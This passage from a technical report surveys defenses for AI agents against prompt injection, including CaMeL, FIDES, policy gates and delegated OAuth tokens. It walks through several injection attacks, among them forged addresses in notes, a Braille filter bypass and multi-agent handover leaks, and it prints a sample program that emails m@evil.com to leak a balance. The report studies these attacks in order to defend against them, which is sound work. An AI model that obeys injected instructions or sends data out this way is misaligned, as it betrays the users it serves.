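Somebody has to write such rules and update them whenever the tools or the business change. If the rules block too much legitimate work, staff will ask for exceptions until the policy is broad again, much as companies left broad permissions in place for people. *Authorization Architectures for Tool-Using AI Agents* (2026) therefore recommends measuring false refusals and the burden on users as well as the number of attacks prevented. Few of the designs here have good figures for false refusals or user burden, and none of those figures come from a company that used a gate for months.

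### What a gate adds to least privilege and to the records

Gates that check the values in a tool call have the best fit, because they can allow a payment to the shop's supplier and refuse the same payment to a thief. No Gmail or Stripe scope in the earlier cases could do this. These gates also limit what the agent can do through its tools, though the token behind the gate keeps all its permissions.

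These checks do less to limit how long an agent keeps a permission or how often it uses it. AC4A's permissions last until someone removes them, so an agent that got write access to move one meeting can later delete another on the same day. More generally, *CreepScope* (2026) distinguishes approving each call from maintaining least privilege over the whole life of a permission. A rule that allows payments of up to $500 to a supplier will also allow a hundred such payments in a row, because each one passes. *ToolFence* limits the number of calls for this reason, and permissions in *AgentCap* expire and allow only a set number of calls.

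A gate can log its decisions for auditing. AC4A's log records when someone created or removed each permission and which permission allowed or blocked each access. An investigator can see why the system let a call through, which Gmail's or Railway's records do not show. The log also includes refused calls, which never reach the outside service. A refused payment to an unknown account could warn the shop about the forged email before the attacker finds a better approach.

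The log doesn't show what prompted a call. SEAgent comes closest because it tracks which tools and agents the information passed through, but it clears this record after each round, so a company would have to save it first. The payment processor's own records would still show only the shop's account. The log also covers only calls that went through the gate, so it could have no record of a deletion like the one at PocketOS.

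## CaMeL: an agent designed around rules for data flow

A gate can check a payment account against a short list that the shop has approved. No such list can cover an email address that nobody could have known in advance, and the best clue is then often where the address came from. *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti et al., 2025) introduced CaMeL, a Google DeepMind design that tracks the origin of every value an agent handles. TechSpot reports that Willison, who coined the term "prompt injection", called CaMeL "the first credible mitigation" that doesn't rely on more AI.

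### Two models, an interpreter and a set of policies

CaMeL builds on Willison's 2023 proposal to split the agent so that the model that decides what to do never reads outside text. As *CaMeLoT* (Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues, 2026) describes it, a planning model receives the user's request and writes a program for the whole task in a restricted form of Python. A reading model handles emails, files and web pages. It can pull out a date or summarize a page, but it has no tools, so an instruction hidden in the page can't make it send anything.

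An interpreter runs the program and makes the tool calls. It labels each value with its sources and the people who may read it. Before each tool call, a policy written as a Python function checks the tool, the arguments and their labels, then allows or refuses the call.

An ordinary agent chooses each action from the prompt p and everything that earlier tool calls returned. CaMeL's planning model writes the program π from the prompt and the tool descriptions D:

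π ~ f( · | p, D )

The text of a stranger's email does not appear on the right-hand side, so it has no influence on which program the model writes.

### Sending Bob a document

Suppose a user asks the agent to send Bob the document he requested in yesterday's meeting, and says that the notes are in the shared drive. The planning model might write this program:

```
notes = get_file("meeting notes")
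address = ask_reader("Find Bob's email address", notes)
name = ask_reader("Which document did Bob request?", notes)
document = get_file(name)
send_email(to=address, attachment=document)
```

The planning model writes the program without having Bob's address or the document's name. The interpreter fills them in and labels them as the program runs.

| Value | Where it came from | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
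| notes | Shared drive | User, Bob, Dana |
| address, name | The notes, through the reading model | User, Bob, Dana |
| document (the budget) | Shared drive, found through the notes | User, Bob |

The budget file itself is open to the user, Bob and Carol. But the agent found it through the notes, so its label combines both, and a combined value may go only to people who may read every part of it:

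{user, Bob, Dana} ∩ {user, Bob, Carol} = {user, Bob}.

Suppose an attacker adds a line to the notes that gives Bob's address as bob@attacker.example and tells the agent to delete last month's invoices. The reading model may treat all of this as true, but it can only return the values the program requests, and the program contains no call that deletes anything. The injected text changes the address but not the sequence of actions.

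The false address then reaches `send_email`. That tool's policy requires every recipient to be a permitted reader of the document. The attacker isn't one, so the interpreter blocks the call or asks the user. EchoLeak got past a check on who may read a document. This policy also checks who may receive it.

The attacker might have more success changing which document the notes name. If the notes list the salary file as the one Bob requested, and Bob works in personnel and has permission to read it, the policy allows the transfer. Bob then receives a file that the user never meant to send.

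A stricter policy could refuse any recipient whose address came from untrusted text. Nikolaou and colleagues give such a policy for direct messages, along with a sample program in which the reading model finds Bob's address in a chat channel and the agent then messages him. The policy would apparently reject this program, so a company can't have both, although each is reasonable.

### What the guarantee covers

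*Can CaMeLs Talk?* (Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues, 2026) calls CaMeL's central guarantee control-flow integrity. This means the agent's actions stay within a plan that depends only on the user's instruction and other trusted information, such as tool descriptions. The paper shares an author with CaMeL.

Outside text can still determine which of the plan's existing branches runs. If the program accepts an invitation when a room is free and declines it otherwise, anyone who can edit the room's calendar can control whether it accepts. This is usually tolerable because the user's request called for both branches.

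A CaMeL plan becomes dangerous when it has a branch for every possible action. In *The LLMbda Calculus*, Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) gave CaMeL a banking task that asked it to read a file and follow the file's instructions precisely. In two runs with CaMeL's policies turned off, the planning model wrote a program that could call whichever tool the file named, and an attack succeeded. The model wrote the program before CaMeL read the file, as CaMeL's guarantee requires, but the attacker could still choose the action.

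Policies are also necessary when an attack uses an action that the task requires. Garby and colleagues sorted 144 pairings of a banking task with an attack. In 97, the attack needed an action that would never appear in the user's program, so fixing the program in advance generally defeats it. In the other 47, the program could already contain the action the attacker needed, such as a payment.

The guarantee assumes that the user's request is trustworthy. *Operationalizing CaMeL* (Tallam and Miller, 2025) points out that a phishing message can trick a user into giving the agent a harmful prompt. The planning model would then read the attacker's text directly, as Copilot did when SearchLeak's link filled in its search box.

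### What it costs in completed tasks

Most published figures for such designs come from AgentDojo, the benchmark used for the SEAgent and Progent results. It gives an agent 97 ordinary tasks in four simulated environments. To test security, it pairs the tasks with attackers' goals, hides instructions in data the agent will read, and checks whether the agent carries them out.

Bhagwatkar, Kasa and colleagues (2025), in *Indirect Prompt Injections*, compare CaMeL's published results for GPT-4o with their own run of an unprotected agent. Without attacks, CaMeL completed 53.6% of tasks and the unprotected agent completed 83.0%. Under attack, CaMeL completed 54.5% and the unprotected agent 50.0%. No attacks succeeded against CaMeL, while 57.7% succeeded against the unprotected agent. Tallam and Miller quote an earlier overall figure of 67% for CaMeL.

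Two other teams ran CaMeL. *SecureClaw* (2026) ran an adapted version in all four environments, and Garby and colleagues ran it on banking tasks with two newer models.

| Test of CaMeL | Tasks completed without an attack | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|---|
| Published results, GPT-4o | 53.6% | 0% |
| *SecureClaw*, adapted version | 29 of 97 (29.9%) | 0 of 629 |
| Garby and colleagues, banking, policies off | 67–71% | 5 of 622 |
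| Garby and colleagues, banking, policies on | 37.5% | 0 of 588 |

The figure from *SecureClaw* may partly reflect the adaptation, and that paper presents a competing system. In the same test, Progent completed 59 tasks, but at least 20 attacks succeeded against it.

Garby and colleagues' comparison is more informative because only the policies changed. Some of their attack runs did not finish, but the share of tasks completed fell sharply for both models, by about 29 and 33 percentage points. Many banking tasks ask the agent to read something and act on it, such as paying a bill stored in a file, so a policy that forbids payments based on untrusted text also blocks tasks like this.

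CaMeL also uses more tokens, the units of text that model providers charge for. Bhagwatkar and colleagues write that the median task took 2.82 times as many input tokens and 2.73 times as many output tokens as with no defense, but the medians in their table give ratios of about 1.8 and 2.2. The averages in that table are 3.6 and 6.1 times as high as with no defense, so a minority of tasks must have used far more tokens than the rest.

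Bhagwatkar and colleagues argue that a much simpler defense does better. They use a second model to remove suspicious instructions from whatever a tool returns. With this filter, GPT-4o completed 74.1% of AgentDojo's tasks and no attacks succeeded. But they also defeated the filter with an attack written in Braille. The filter translated the Braille into English and passed it on, and the agent booked the hotel that the attacker wanted. CaMeL's planning model never receives the text, so it doesn't matter how an attacker encodes it. A score of zero on AgentDojo's fixed attacks can't distinguish the two defenses, but only CaMeL's structure gives a reason to expect it to stop new attacks.

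CaMeL reduces task completion less when agents use better models. Peters-Gill and colleagues tested it without policies on a benchmark of industrial maintenance work. Agents with CaMeL completed 21.6 percentage points fewer tasks than unprotected agents on average across five models, but only 13.4 points fewer with the two strongest, GPT-5.5 and Claude Fable 5. CaMeL's measured security benefit also shrinks with better models. On a version of AgentDojo for several cooperating agents, no attack succeeded against GPT-5.5 even without CaMeL. Peters-Gill and colleagues warn that this does not mean the model is immune, because a large public competition found successful attacks on every frontier model tested.

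### When the plan depends on what the agent reads

Peters-Gill and colleagues found that most of the failed tasks were caused by writing the program before seeing any data. In several cases, an agent requested data about one machine or period and received data about a similar one. An ordinary agent might have noticed the mismatch, but the program had no check for it and continued running.

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, define the tasks that don't have this problem. Let S(d) be the set of action sequences that complete a task when the data is d. The task is data-independent if at least one sequence works whatever the data turns out to be:

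⋂ S(d) ≠ ∅, taken over every possible d.

Forwarding the three latest emails to a colleague is a data-independent task, because the steps are the same whatever the emails contain. Completing everything on a to-do list is data-dependent, because the list determines the steps. Costa and colleagues classify 5% of AgentDojo's office tasks as data-dependent, compared with more than 40% of its banking and Slack tasks.

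CaMeL can handle such a task if the planning model foresees the possibilities and writes a branch for each. FIDES, the system Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, is more flexible because it lets the planning model choose its next step after each result. Like CaMeL, it labels data and hides untrusted text from that model, but the model can open a hidden text if necessary. Once the model has opened one, FIDES treats its later decisions as untrusted, and the policies block consequential actions such as payments.

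FIDES also lets the planning model learn limited information about a text without reading it. For example, the planning model can ask the reading model whether an email requests a meeting and accept only yes or no. An attacker can make the answer wrong, but a yes or no can't carry an instruction to send files to a stranger. A policy can therefore allow the agent to create a calendar event if the answer is yes.

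With GPT-4o and policies on, FIDES completed about 50% of tasks, averaged over the four environments. An ordinary agent scored 8 points lower under the same policies but completed about 84% of tasks without them. Costa and colleagues judged that no real attack succeeded against FIDES with its policies on. This result follows partly from the test setup, because they marked as untrusted exactly the fields that AgentDojo's attacks use. A company doesn't know in advance which fields attackers will use. They also left the restricted answers out of this test, so it doesn't show how much those answers help.

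### Wrong content and indirect leaks

A label records where a value came from but not whether it is true. Costa and colleagues give the example of an email containing an instruction for the reading model to produce an empty summary. The agent then sends that summary to the right person with the right tool, without violating any policy.

The same weakness can cost money. One AgentDojo task asks the agent to make a payment described in a file, and the attack replaces the file's contents with a different payment request. According to Garby and colleagues, this was one of two attacks that succeeded in CaMeL's original evaluation, and Debenedetti and colleagues consider it outside the threats CaMeL addresses. In the other attack, the agent quoted hotel reviews word for word, and the benchmark counted the attacker's words in the quotation as a successful attack.

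Tallam and Miller add that CaMeL does not inspect the agent's final answer. FIDES does not check answers either, though Costa and colleagues explain how to add a check. A company would need such a check to defend against EchoLeak, which sent data out through an image in Copilot's answer.

Information can also leak through the agent's behavior. Tallam and Miller describe a program that contacts a website as many times as a secret number, so that the site's owner learns the number by counting visits. Garby and colleagues found a subtler leak in the way CaMeL's interpreter assigns labels. A short program like this one shows the problem:

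```
rich = True
low = True
if balance > threshold: low = False
if low: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

If the balance is high, the assignment in the fourth line doesn't run, so the interpreter never marks `rich` as depending on the secret balance. It then allows the email, which reveals that the balance is high.

An attacker normally can't write the program in CaMeL, so this leak would require the planning model to produce such code by accident. Another flaw that Garby and colleagues mention seems more likely to matter in practice. The interpreter treats an untrusted value as trusted when a program inserts it into a longer piece of text, which programs do routinely.

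Garby and colleagues' alternative is LLMbda, a small programming language with computer-checked proofs that its label tracking has no gaps of this kind. Their agent completed 75% of the banking tasks with GPT-5.2 while always enforcing its policies. Across three models, 2 of 1,296 attacks succeeded, and both used the replaced payment file.

The agent completes as many tasks as it does partly because its planning model can declare in advance that the program may act on a particular untrusted file. Removing this option lowered the share of tasks completed with Qwen3.7-plus from 75% to 62.5%, but it also stopped the payment attack. Proofs can remove accidental leaks, but an agent allowed to pay a real bill from a file could also pay a forged one.

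### Who writes the policies and answers the prompts

Somebody has to write a policy for every tool. Tallam and Miller warn that a company with hundreds of tools will accumulate duplicated and inconsistent rules. Their paper is a weak source, and even its reference for CaMeL points to a different work. But the concern is sensible, because companies already struggle to maintain much simpler permissions for their staff.

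CaMeL's policies also apply to only one call at a time. A security team may want a rule about the whole task, such as requiring a person's approval before the agent disconnects a computer from the network. Nikolaou and colleagues' extension, CaMeLoT, turns the program into a map of its possible steps and checks the map against such rules before anything runs. If it finds a path that breaks a rule, it describes the path to the planning model, which tries to repair the program. CaMeLoT sometimes rejects safe programs because it assumes that loops could run any number of times.

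When a policy blocks a tool call, the agent can ask the user for approval, and TechSpot notes that frequent requests could frustrate users. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, argue that ordinary agents have the same problem. In benchmarks, unprotected agents act without asking, but products such as GitHub Copilot ask before most consequential actions. A fair comparison should therefore count approvals as well as completed tasks.

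This comparison used AgentDojo with OpenAI's o3-mini. An ordinary agent that asks before every consequential action needed about 48 approvals for the tasks it completed, while FIDES needed about 19. Without any approvals, the ordinary agent completed 24.3% of tasks, and FIDES completed 50.1%. PRUDENTIA, an extension of FIDES that tells the planning model the policies, completed 59.1%. These results are good evidence against the claim that data rules only make agents less useful, at least for companies that would otherwise review each action.

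PRUDENTIA can also ask the user to vouch for a whole text. If an email lists ten jobs, the user approves the email once instead of approving each job. Fewer prompts should mean less fatigue, but each answer matters more, because a user who vouches for the email without reading it also approves any job an attacker added to the list. Kolluri and colleagues assumed that people would reject malicious requests and did not test this with real users.

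### When one agent instructs another

CaMeL's guarantee applies to a single agent, and Peters-Gill and colleagues show that it can fail when several agents work together. They asked three CaMeL agents to send a summary of job applicants to Julie on Slack. One agent coordinated, another read the database and the third sent messages. The database contained an instruction to email the applicants' data to an outside address.

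The database agent and the coordinator both correctly handled this text as data. The coordinator then put the summary into its request to the messaging agent. That agent treated the whole request as its user's instruction, so its planning model read the attacker's text and wrote a program that also sent the email. The ServiceNow ticket attack used a similar handover.

Their remedy, multi-CaMeL, splits each request into two parts. One holds instructions and may not contain anything that came from a tool. The other holds data, which keeps its labels and stays hidden from the receiving agent's planning model. On the multi-agent version of AgentDojo, an average of 12.9% of attacks succeeded with no defense, 0.2% with separate CaMeL agents and none with multi-CaMeL. These tests used no data policies. Multi-CaMeL also inherits the flaws in CaMeL's label tracking, and it covers agents arranged in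 a hierarchy, not those that communicate freely with each other.

### A new agent around old tools

CaMeL is clearly an agent-first design, because it assumes that outside text will mislead any model that reads it. It is also a wrapper. Tallam and Miller describe it as a layer around an unmodified language model, and its interpreter can call existing tools, which may include a Gmail connection whose token can read all of a user's mail and send mail as that user.

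A program in CaMeL can act only through the tools that the interpreter provides. If it found a stored key, as the PocketOS agent did, the key would be another labeled value, and the program could use it to contact Railway only if a tool allowed that. A developer who adds a tool for running arbitrary commands gives up most of this protection.

Like a gate, though, the wrapper leaves the token itself as powerful as before.

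The labels also have to be added, because a mail service doesn't mark which fields of a message are trusted or who may read it. In their tests, Costa and colleagues wrote functions around the existing tools to add this information, and treated an email's sender and recipients as its permitted readers. This rule is sensible for email, but permitted readers are harder to determine for files on a shared drive. If somebody has shared the salary file with the whole company by mistake, a label copied from the drive's settings will permit the agent to send it to any employee. CaMeL's rules would then allow the same oversharing that Copilot exposed.

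The rules are also hard to apply to an agent that works by looking at a screen and clicking. *CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (2026) adapts the fixed plan to such agents, but it leaves out the data policies and instead limits how the program may use the reading model.

### The program as a permission and as a record

CaMeL does better on least privilege than any of the retrofitted agents. The program works as a permission written for one task, because once it starts, outside text can trigger only the calls it contains. If π is the program, an attacker can at most cause

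{ calls in π, with values that the policies allow }.

This set is much smaller than what the token permits, and it disappears when the program ends. The policies also improve fit, because they can let the agent send the budget to Bob but not to a stranger. But a model writes the program, which can include more calls than the task needs if the request is ambiguous or the plan is careless. The underlying token still fails on range and duration.

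Unlike ordinary logs, the program shows an auditor what the agent planned to do before it read any outside text. If Bob receives the wrong file, an investigator can see that the user's request led to the email and that the file's name came from the meeting notes. With an ordinary agent, the investigator would know only that the agent read the notes and then sent the file.

In CaMeL, it is therefore much clearer which inputs acted as instructions, the question Siu and colleagues raised. The user's request determined which actions the agent took, except where outside text selected a branch. The labels don't show which sentence in the notes misled the reading model, so the investigator also needs a copy of the notes as they were at the time.

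If the interpreter wrongly treats a value as trusted, it will also record the value as trusted, and the investigator may rule out the real cause. Garby and colleagues add that CaMeL's labeling rules exist only as Python code, which makes them hard to audit. The company must also choose to keep the programs and labels, because Google's own records would show only an email from the user's account.

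## Agent identities and short-lived delegated tokens

A mail provider or file store can only record that an agent acted if the request contains that information. Several companies and standards bodies are therefore working on identities for agents, and on tokens that name both the agent and the person it works for.

### One deletion, two log entries

Suppose Maria asks an agent to clear duplicate reports from her finance team's shared folder, and the agent deletes the quarterly forecast. The agent uses a stored key that two colleagues and a nightly script also use. The file store's log might contain this invented entry:

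```
14:02:07  DELETE /finance/q3-forecast.xlsx
          key:      finance-shared
```

An investigator can see when the file disappeared, but not whether a colleague, the script or the agent deleted it. If the agent had used Maria's login, the entry would show her name, which is more misleading. In both cases the agent and the people send the same credential, so the file store cannot tell them apart. *Back to the Future*, an August 2026 post from the US standards institute NIST, warns that a static key does not prove identity.

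With a token made for the purpose, the entry could look like this:

```
14:02:07  DELETE /finance/q3-forecast.xlsx
          for:      maria@firm.example
          by:       filing-agent-07
          task:     4471, clear duplicate reports
          allowed:  delete files in /finance
          expires:  14:10:00
```

The investigator now knows which agent's session to open and has no reason to suspect Maria of deleting the file by hand. But the file store deleted the file because the token allowed the agent to delete anything in the folder.

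### How the agent gets the token

The usual mechanism is a standard called RFC 8693, which predates language model agents. Jones, Nadalin and colleagues, in *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange*, define how a program can trade one token for another. For Maria's agent, the exchange would work like this:

1. The company registers the agent under its own name, separately from any employee.
2. Maria signs in, and the agent receives a token that represents her.
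3. The agent sends the company's authorization server Maria's token and a second token that represents the agent. It also names the service it wants to use and the scopes it needs.
4. The server checks both tokens, decides whether this agent may act for Maria, and issues a new token with an expiry time.
5. The agent presents the new token to the file store.

In the new token, the `sub` field names Maria and the `act` field, short for "actor", names the agent. The standard defines no field for the task, so the company would have to add one.

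The second token in step 3 is optional. If the agent sends only Maria's token, the file store can't distinguish the agent from Maria, which Jones and colleagues call impersonation. A product can therefore use token exchange with narrow scopes and short lifetimes and still produce a log that attributes the agent's actions to Maria.

Naming both parties also spares a company the choice that ServiceNow's customers faced, between running an agent as the user and giving it an account of its own. A service that receives both names can require both to have permission:

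allowed = A(Maria) ∩ A(agent) ∩ scopes in the token.

The standard makes this possible but leaves the rule to whoever runs the servers.

It also lets an agent carelessly request more access than it needs. An agent that requests several scopes at several services in one token is requesting every scope at every service. For example, an agent that needs to read mail and write to a calendar might request "read" and "write" at both services, which would also allow it to write mail. Using a separate token for each service would avoid this.

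The short lifetime matters because canceling Maria's original token does not automatically cancel the one the agent got in exchange. The standard's example tokens last one minute and one hour. A thief can use an ordinary token until it expires, but NIST points to a protection called Demonstrated Proof-of-Possession, which ties a token to a cryptographic key that the sender must also have. This would stop a thief who copied only the tokens, but not one who controlled the server that held both the tokens and the key.

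### Passing on less at each handover

Maria's agent might ask a second agent to compare the reports and find the duplicates. The second agent needs to read files but not delete them, so it should get a token with less authority. If Sₖ is the authority of the k-th agent in a chain, the aim is

S₁ ⊇ S₂ ⊇ S₃ ⊇ …

This rule could have stopped the ServiceNow ticket attack. An agent with permission only to categorize one ticket would have had no access to a confidential ticket and so could not have passed that access on. The more powerful agent it called therefore could not have fetched the confidential text for it.

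RFC 8693 supports narrower tokens but does not require them. A token can record a chain of delegation by nesting one `act` field inside another, but a service must base its access decision only on the person and the current agent; earlier agents are listed for information. In a June 2026 draft, *Cryptographically Verifiable Actor Chains for OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange*, Prasad, Krishnan and colleagues point out that the standard also lacks common rules for preserving and checking the chain. An investigator may therefore find that some agents are missing from it.

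An agent also has to contact the authorization server each time it wants a narrower token. *Control the Chain, Secure the System* (Kolhe, 2026) describes formats such as Macaroons and Biscuits, which let a token's holder add restrictions but not remove them. In March 2026, no major identity provider supported either format natively.

Kolhe, who works on agent security at the identity company Okta, illustrates the need for narrowed tokens with a demonstration by the research team Unit 42. A financial assistant asked a research agent for market news. The reply contained hidden instructions, and the assistant bought ten shares without telling its user. Kolhe argues that a narrowed token would have blocked the research agent from buying shares. But in the demonstration the financial assistant bought them with its own authority, so narrowing the research agent's token would not have prevented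 the purchase. A narrowed token limits what an agent can do itself, but does not stop it from misleading another agent.

### What companies can use now

| Part | Status in late 2026 |
|---|---|
| Token exchange with an actor field | Published standard, with the actor optional |
| Microsoft's agent identities | Shipped, with some parts in preview |
| MCP authorization | Published specification, optional for MCP software |
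| Central company control of MCP connections | Stable extension, also optional |
| Common formats for agents' names and delegation chains | Drafts |
| NIST's agent identity project | Draft concept paper, with the project still in planning |

#### Microsoft Entra

Microsoft has made agent identities generally available in Entra, its system for managing accounts and sign-ins, though the setup wizard for creating them is still a preview. Each agent has its own ID and can have a sponsor, the person or group accountable for it. A template called a blueprint holds the credentials and requests tokens for all the agents made from it, so the agents themselves hold no passwords or keys.

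In an example from Microsoft, several sales teams each deploy a copy of the same assistant. Each copy has a separate identity, and an administrator can disable all of them at once. But permissions granted to their shared blueprint pass to every copy, so they suit a type of agent rather than a single task. Someone who stole the blueprint's credentials could presumably request tokens for all the copies that work without a user.

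Microsoft's *Agent OAuth flows* describes how an agent acting for an employee exchanges the employee's token, much as in Maria's case. The new token identifies both the agent and the employee, but in Microsoft's own fields instead of `act`. To address such differences, *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation* (McGuinness, 2026), an April draft, proposes a common format. Auth0, an identity service owned by Okta, has already adopted parts of the draft, and its tokens can record a chain of up to five handovers.

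"Short-lived" can also mean different things. A sample token in Microsoft's documentation, for an agent working without a user, expires just over eight hours (29,100 seconds) after it is issued. Agents that act for users can get refresh tokens for background work, which let them request new access tokens when the old ones expire, so an agent's authority can last much longer than any single token.

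Older software makes agents harder to identify in audit logs. Some systems accept only ordinary user accounts, so Microsoft lets companies give an agent a second account of that kind, whose activity is logged as user events. As of June 2026, Microsoft's FAQ states that audit logs do not distinguish agents by default and tells investigators to look up each ID. Another Microsoft page describes an `agentType` field that marks agents. Microsoft's *Extend Sign-In Log Monitoring to Cover Agent Identity Traffic* says companies also have to update their alerts because existing rules do not recognize the new values.

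Microsoft's July 2026 guidance recommends giving each agent a stable identity, with a named owner and roles based on tasks, and putting time limits on the permissions instead of on the identity. Each service should check the agent's permissions again on every call. The log should include the agent, its role and scope, the resource, the action, the user it acted for and an ID that links the steps. This would give other agents the separation that Microsoft's logs already make for Copilot. The product does not require these measures, so a company can deploy an agent without them.

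#### The Model Context Protocol

Model Context Protocol's *Authorization* (2026, July 28 version) makes authorization optional and covers servers that agents reach over the web. A server that runs on the user's computer and exchanges text directly with the agent's program should instead take its credentials from its environment, which can mean a stored key.

For web servers that do use it, the specification limits each token to one server. That server must reject tokens meant for others and must not pass them on. A malicious server therefore can't take a token it receives and use it at another server that follows the rules.

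Least privilege is recommended but not required. The client, the program that connects the agent to the server, should request the scopes the server specifies for the current operation. If the server specifies none, the client requests every scope on the server's published list, which is supposed to be short.

When a later call needs more, the server refuses it and names the missing scopes Cₙ. The client then asks for a new token with

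Sₙ₊₁ = Sₙ ∪ Cₙ.

This saves users from approving the same scope repeatedly, but permissions accumulate. An agent that needed to write one file keeps write access even if it only reads files afterward. A stricter client could drop the extra scope after the call, but users would then face more approval requests.

Tabata (2026), in *Authorization in MCP 2026-07-28*, writes that the revision introduces no fundamentally new authorization concepts and mostly clarifies how to apply existing OAuth practice. The core specification doesn't list RFC 8693 among its standards, so an MCP server can follow the specification and still receive a token that doesn't name the agent as an actor.

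An optional extension, stable since June 2026 (Carleton, 2026, *Enterprise-Managed Authorization*), does use token exchange. It lets a company decide centrally which MCP servers its employees can connect to, without a consent screen for each one. Atlassian, which makes workplace software, supports the extension in private beta but still issues its own tokens with its own scopes. The employer therefore controls who can connect, but Atlassian's scopes determine how finely it can limit their access. Removing the consent screens spares employees a decision they often make carelessly, but it makes the administrator's initial choice more important.

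#### NIST

In February 2026, Booth, Fisher and colleagues published *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*, a draft concept paper for a possible project at NIST's cybersecurity center (NCCoE). The paper received more than 600 formal responses, according to Identiverse's *Advancing Standards for Agent Identity*, the listing for a November talk, which still described the project as planned. According to the NCCoE's project page, *Software and SI Agent Identity and Authorization* ("SI" stands for "super intelligence"), the center is still collecting comments on the scope and has not decided whether to build a demonstration.

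In its August post, NIST writes that companies can already use OAuth and other established standards to give agents separate identities and tightly scoped tokens. It expects consumer services to find this harder, because a shop has little control over a customer's agent and may not be able to tell it apart from the customer. Work on credentials that link a consumer's agent to its owner is still at an early stage.

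### The receiving software sets the limit

A token can restrict an agent only in ways that the receiving software checks. Let N be the access a task needs and F the set of permissions the software can enforce. The narrowest useful token then grants

the smallest P in F such that N ⊆ P.

Suppose an old mail server can enforce only two permissions, "read mail" and "read and send mail". If the agent needs to read one thread from Maria's landlord, the smallest sufficient permission is "read mail", which gives access to the whole mailbox. The authorization server could add a field limiting the token to that thread, but the mail server would ignore a field it doesn't support.

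Giving the agent its own identity would still improve the record, but only if the mail server logs that identity. A server that reads only the `sub` field would log Maria's name, as before. The company would then have to rely on the authorization server's record, which could show that the agent obtained a token for Maria's mail at 14:01 but not which messages it read.

The same limit applies to the earlier cases. Railway had no permission that covered only domain changes, and Supabase's tokens had no per-table permissions, so a separate identity system could not have added those restrictions. An expiry time would have helped at PocketOS, where the token still worked after the job it was made for was finished.

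Somebody therefore has to change the receiving software or put a gateway in front of it. NIST mentions Rich Authorization Requests, a standard that lets a program ask for more specific permissions than a traditional scope can express, but the service must still be able to enforce them.

Even adding the agent's name can require changes to the receiving service. Auth0 leaves out the fields that mark a caller as an AI agent unless the service opts in, and warns that services may need updates to handle those fields.

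### How many companies can trace their agents?

A survey of 1,100 IT and security decision-makers suggests that many companies have only a partial record of what their AI agents do. *AI agent permissions are outrunning security* (Zorz, October 2026) reports that 84% of respondents claimed visibility into how their AI systems access data and other systems, but only 49% said they could see and audit every action an agent takes. It also reports that 70% let AI make decisions or take actions that would have needed human approval a year earlier.

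The sponsor appears to be Illumio, a security company whose vice president comments on the results throughout Zorz's article. Illumio sells software that limits which systems can reach one another, so it benefits if companies worry about what their agents can reach.

The 84% and 49% figures may be consistent, because a company can have a general view of its agents' access and still miss some actions. The 49% may be too high, because respondents reported what they believed and nobody tested their logs. In 2025, for example, Microsoft's customers could reasonably have believed that their logs listed every file Copilot read.

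The survey also found that only a quarter of respondents listed an explicit definition of what an agent may do among their two main controls. A company needs that definition before it can write it into a token. Without it, a company that adopts agent identities will probably give each agent its own name but the same broad permissions as before.

### The missing text

Maria's log entry records the person, the agent and the task, but not why the agent deleted the forecast. The entry would be the same whether the agent misjudged which files were duplicates or followed a deletion instruction in one of the folder's documents.

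A delegated token has no field for an outsider, such as the person who sent the EchoLeak email, because that person never requested access. Microsoft's list of recommended log fields also omits the text the agent read. The ID that links the steps would help an investigator find that text if the company had kept it.

Keeping a record that explains every agent action creates a serious privacy risk, because the company would have to store the emails, files and web pages that each agent read, and its users' requests. A mail agent's log would duplicate much of the mailbox, including messages from people who never dealt with the agent. Employees may have written about illness or pay, and they may not know that a copy remains after they delete the original. An intruder who reached the log would get all of it in one place.

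Jones and colleagues advise putting only the minimum necessary data in a token, so the text the agent read belongs in a separate store with tighter access and a fixed deletion date. A company could instead keep a cryptographic fingerprint of each document, which takes up little space and can confirm whether a document that still exists is the version the agent read. But a fingerprint can't recover text that someone has changed or deleted, as happened to the malicious description in the ServiceNow ticket attack. To investigate such attacks, companies will have to keep some of the text itself, perhaps only for consequential actions such as payments and deletions.

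### Effects on access and records

These tokens support least privilege most by limiting duration. The agent's authority ends when the token expires, without anyone having to revoke it, unless a refresh token renews it. Range improves only as far as the receiving software allows. Fit improves least, because an agent with permission to delete files in a folder can delete the forecast as well as the duplicates. A company would still need per-call checks to distinguish them.

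Delegated tokens can be much better than a shared login or key for auditing who acted. Railway's MCP server requires a user's identity for its audit trail, but adding the agent's name would also distinguish the user's own actions from the agent's. An investigator could use a linking ID to follow one task across several companies' logs, if those companies record the ID.

These gains disappear if Maria's agent finds and uses the old `finance-shared` key, because the next deletion will again appear in the log under that key alone.
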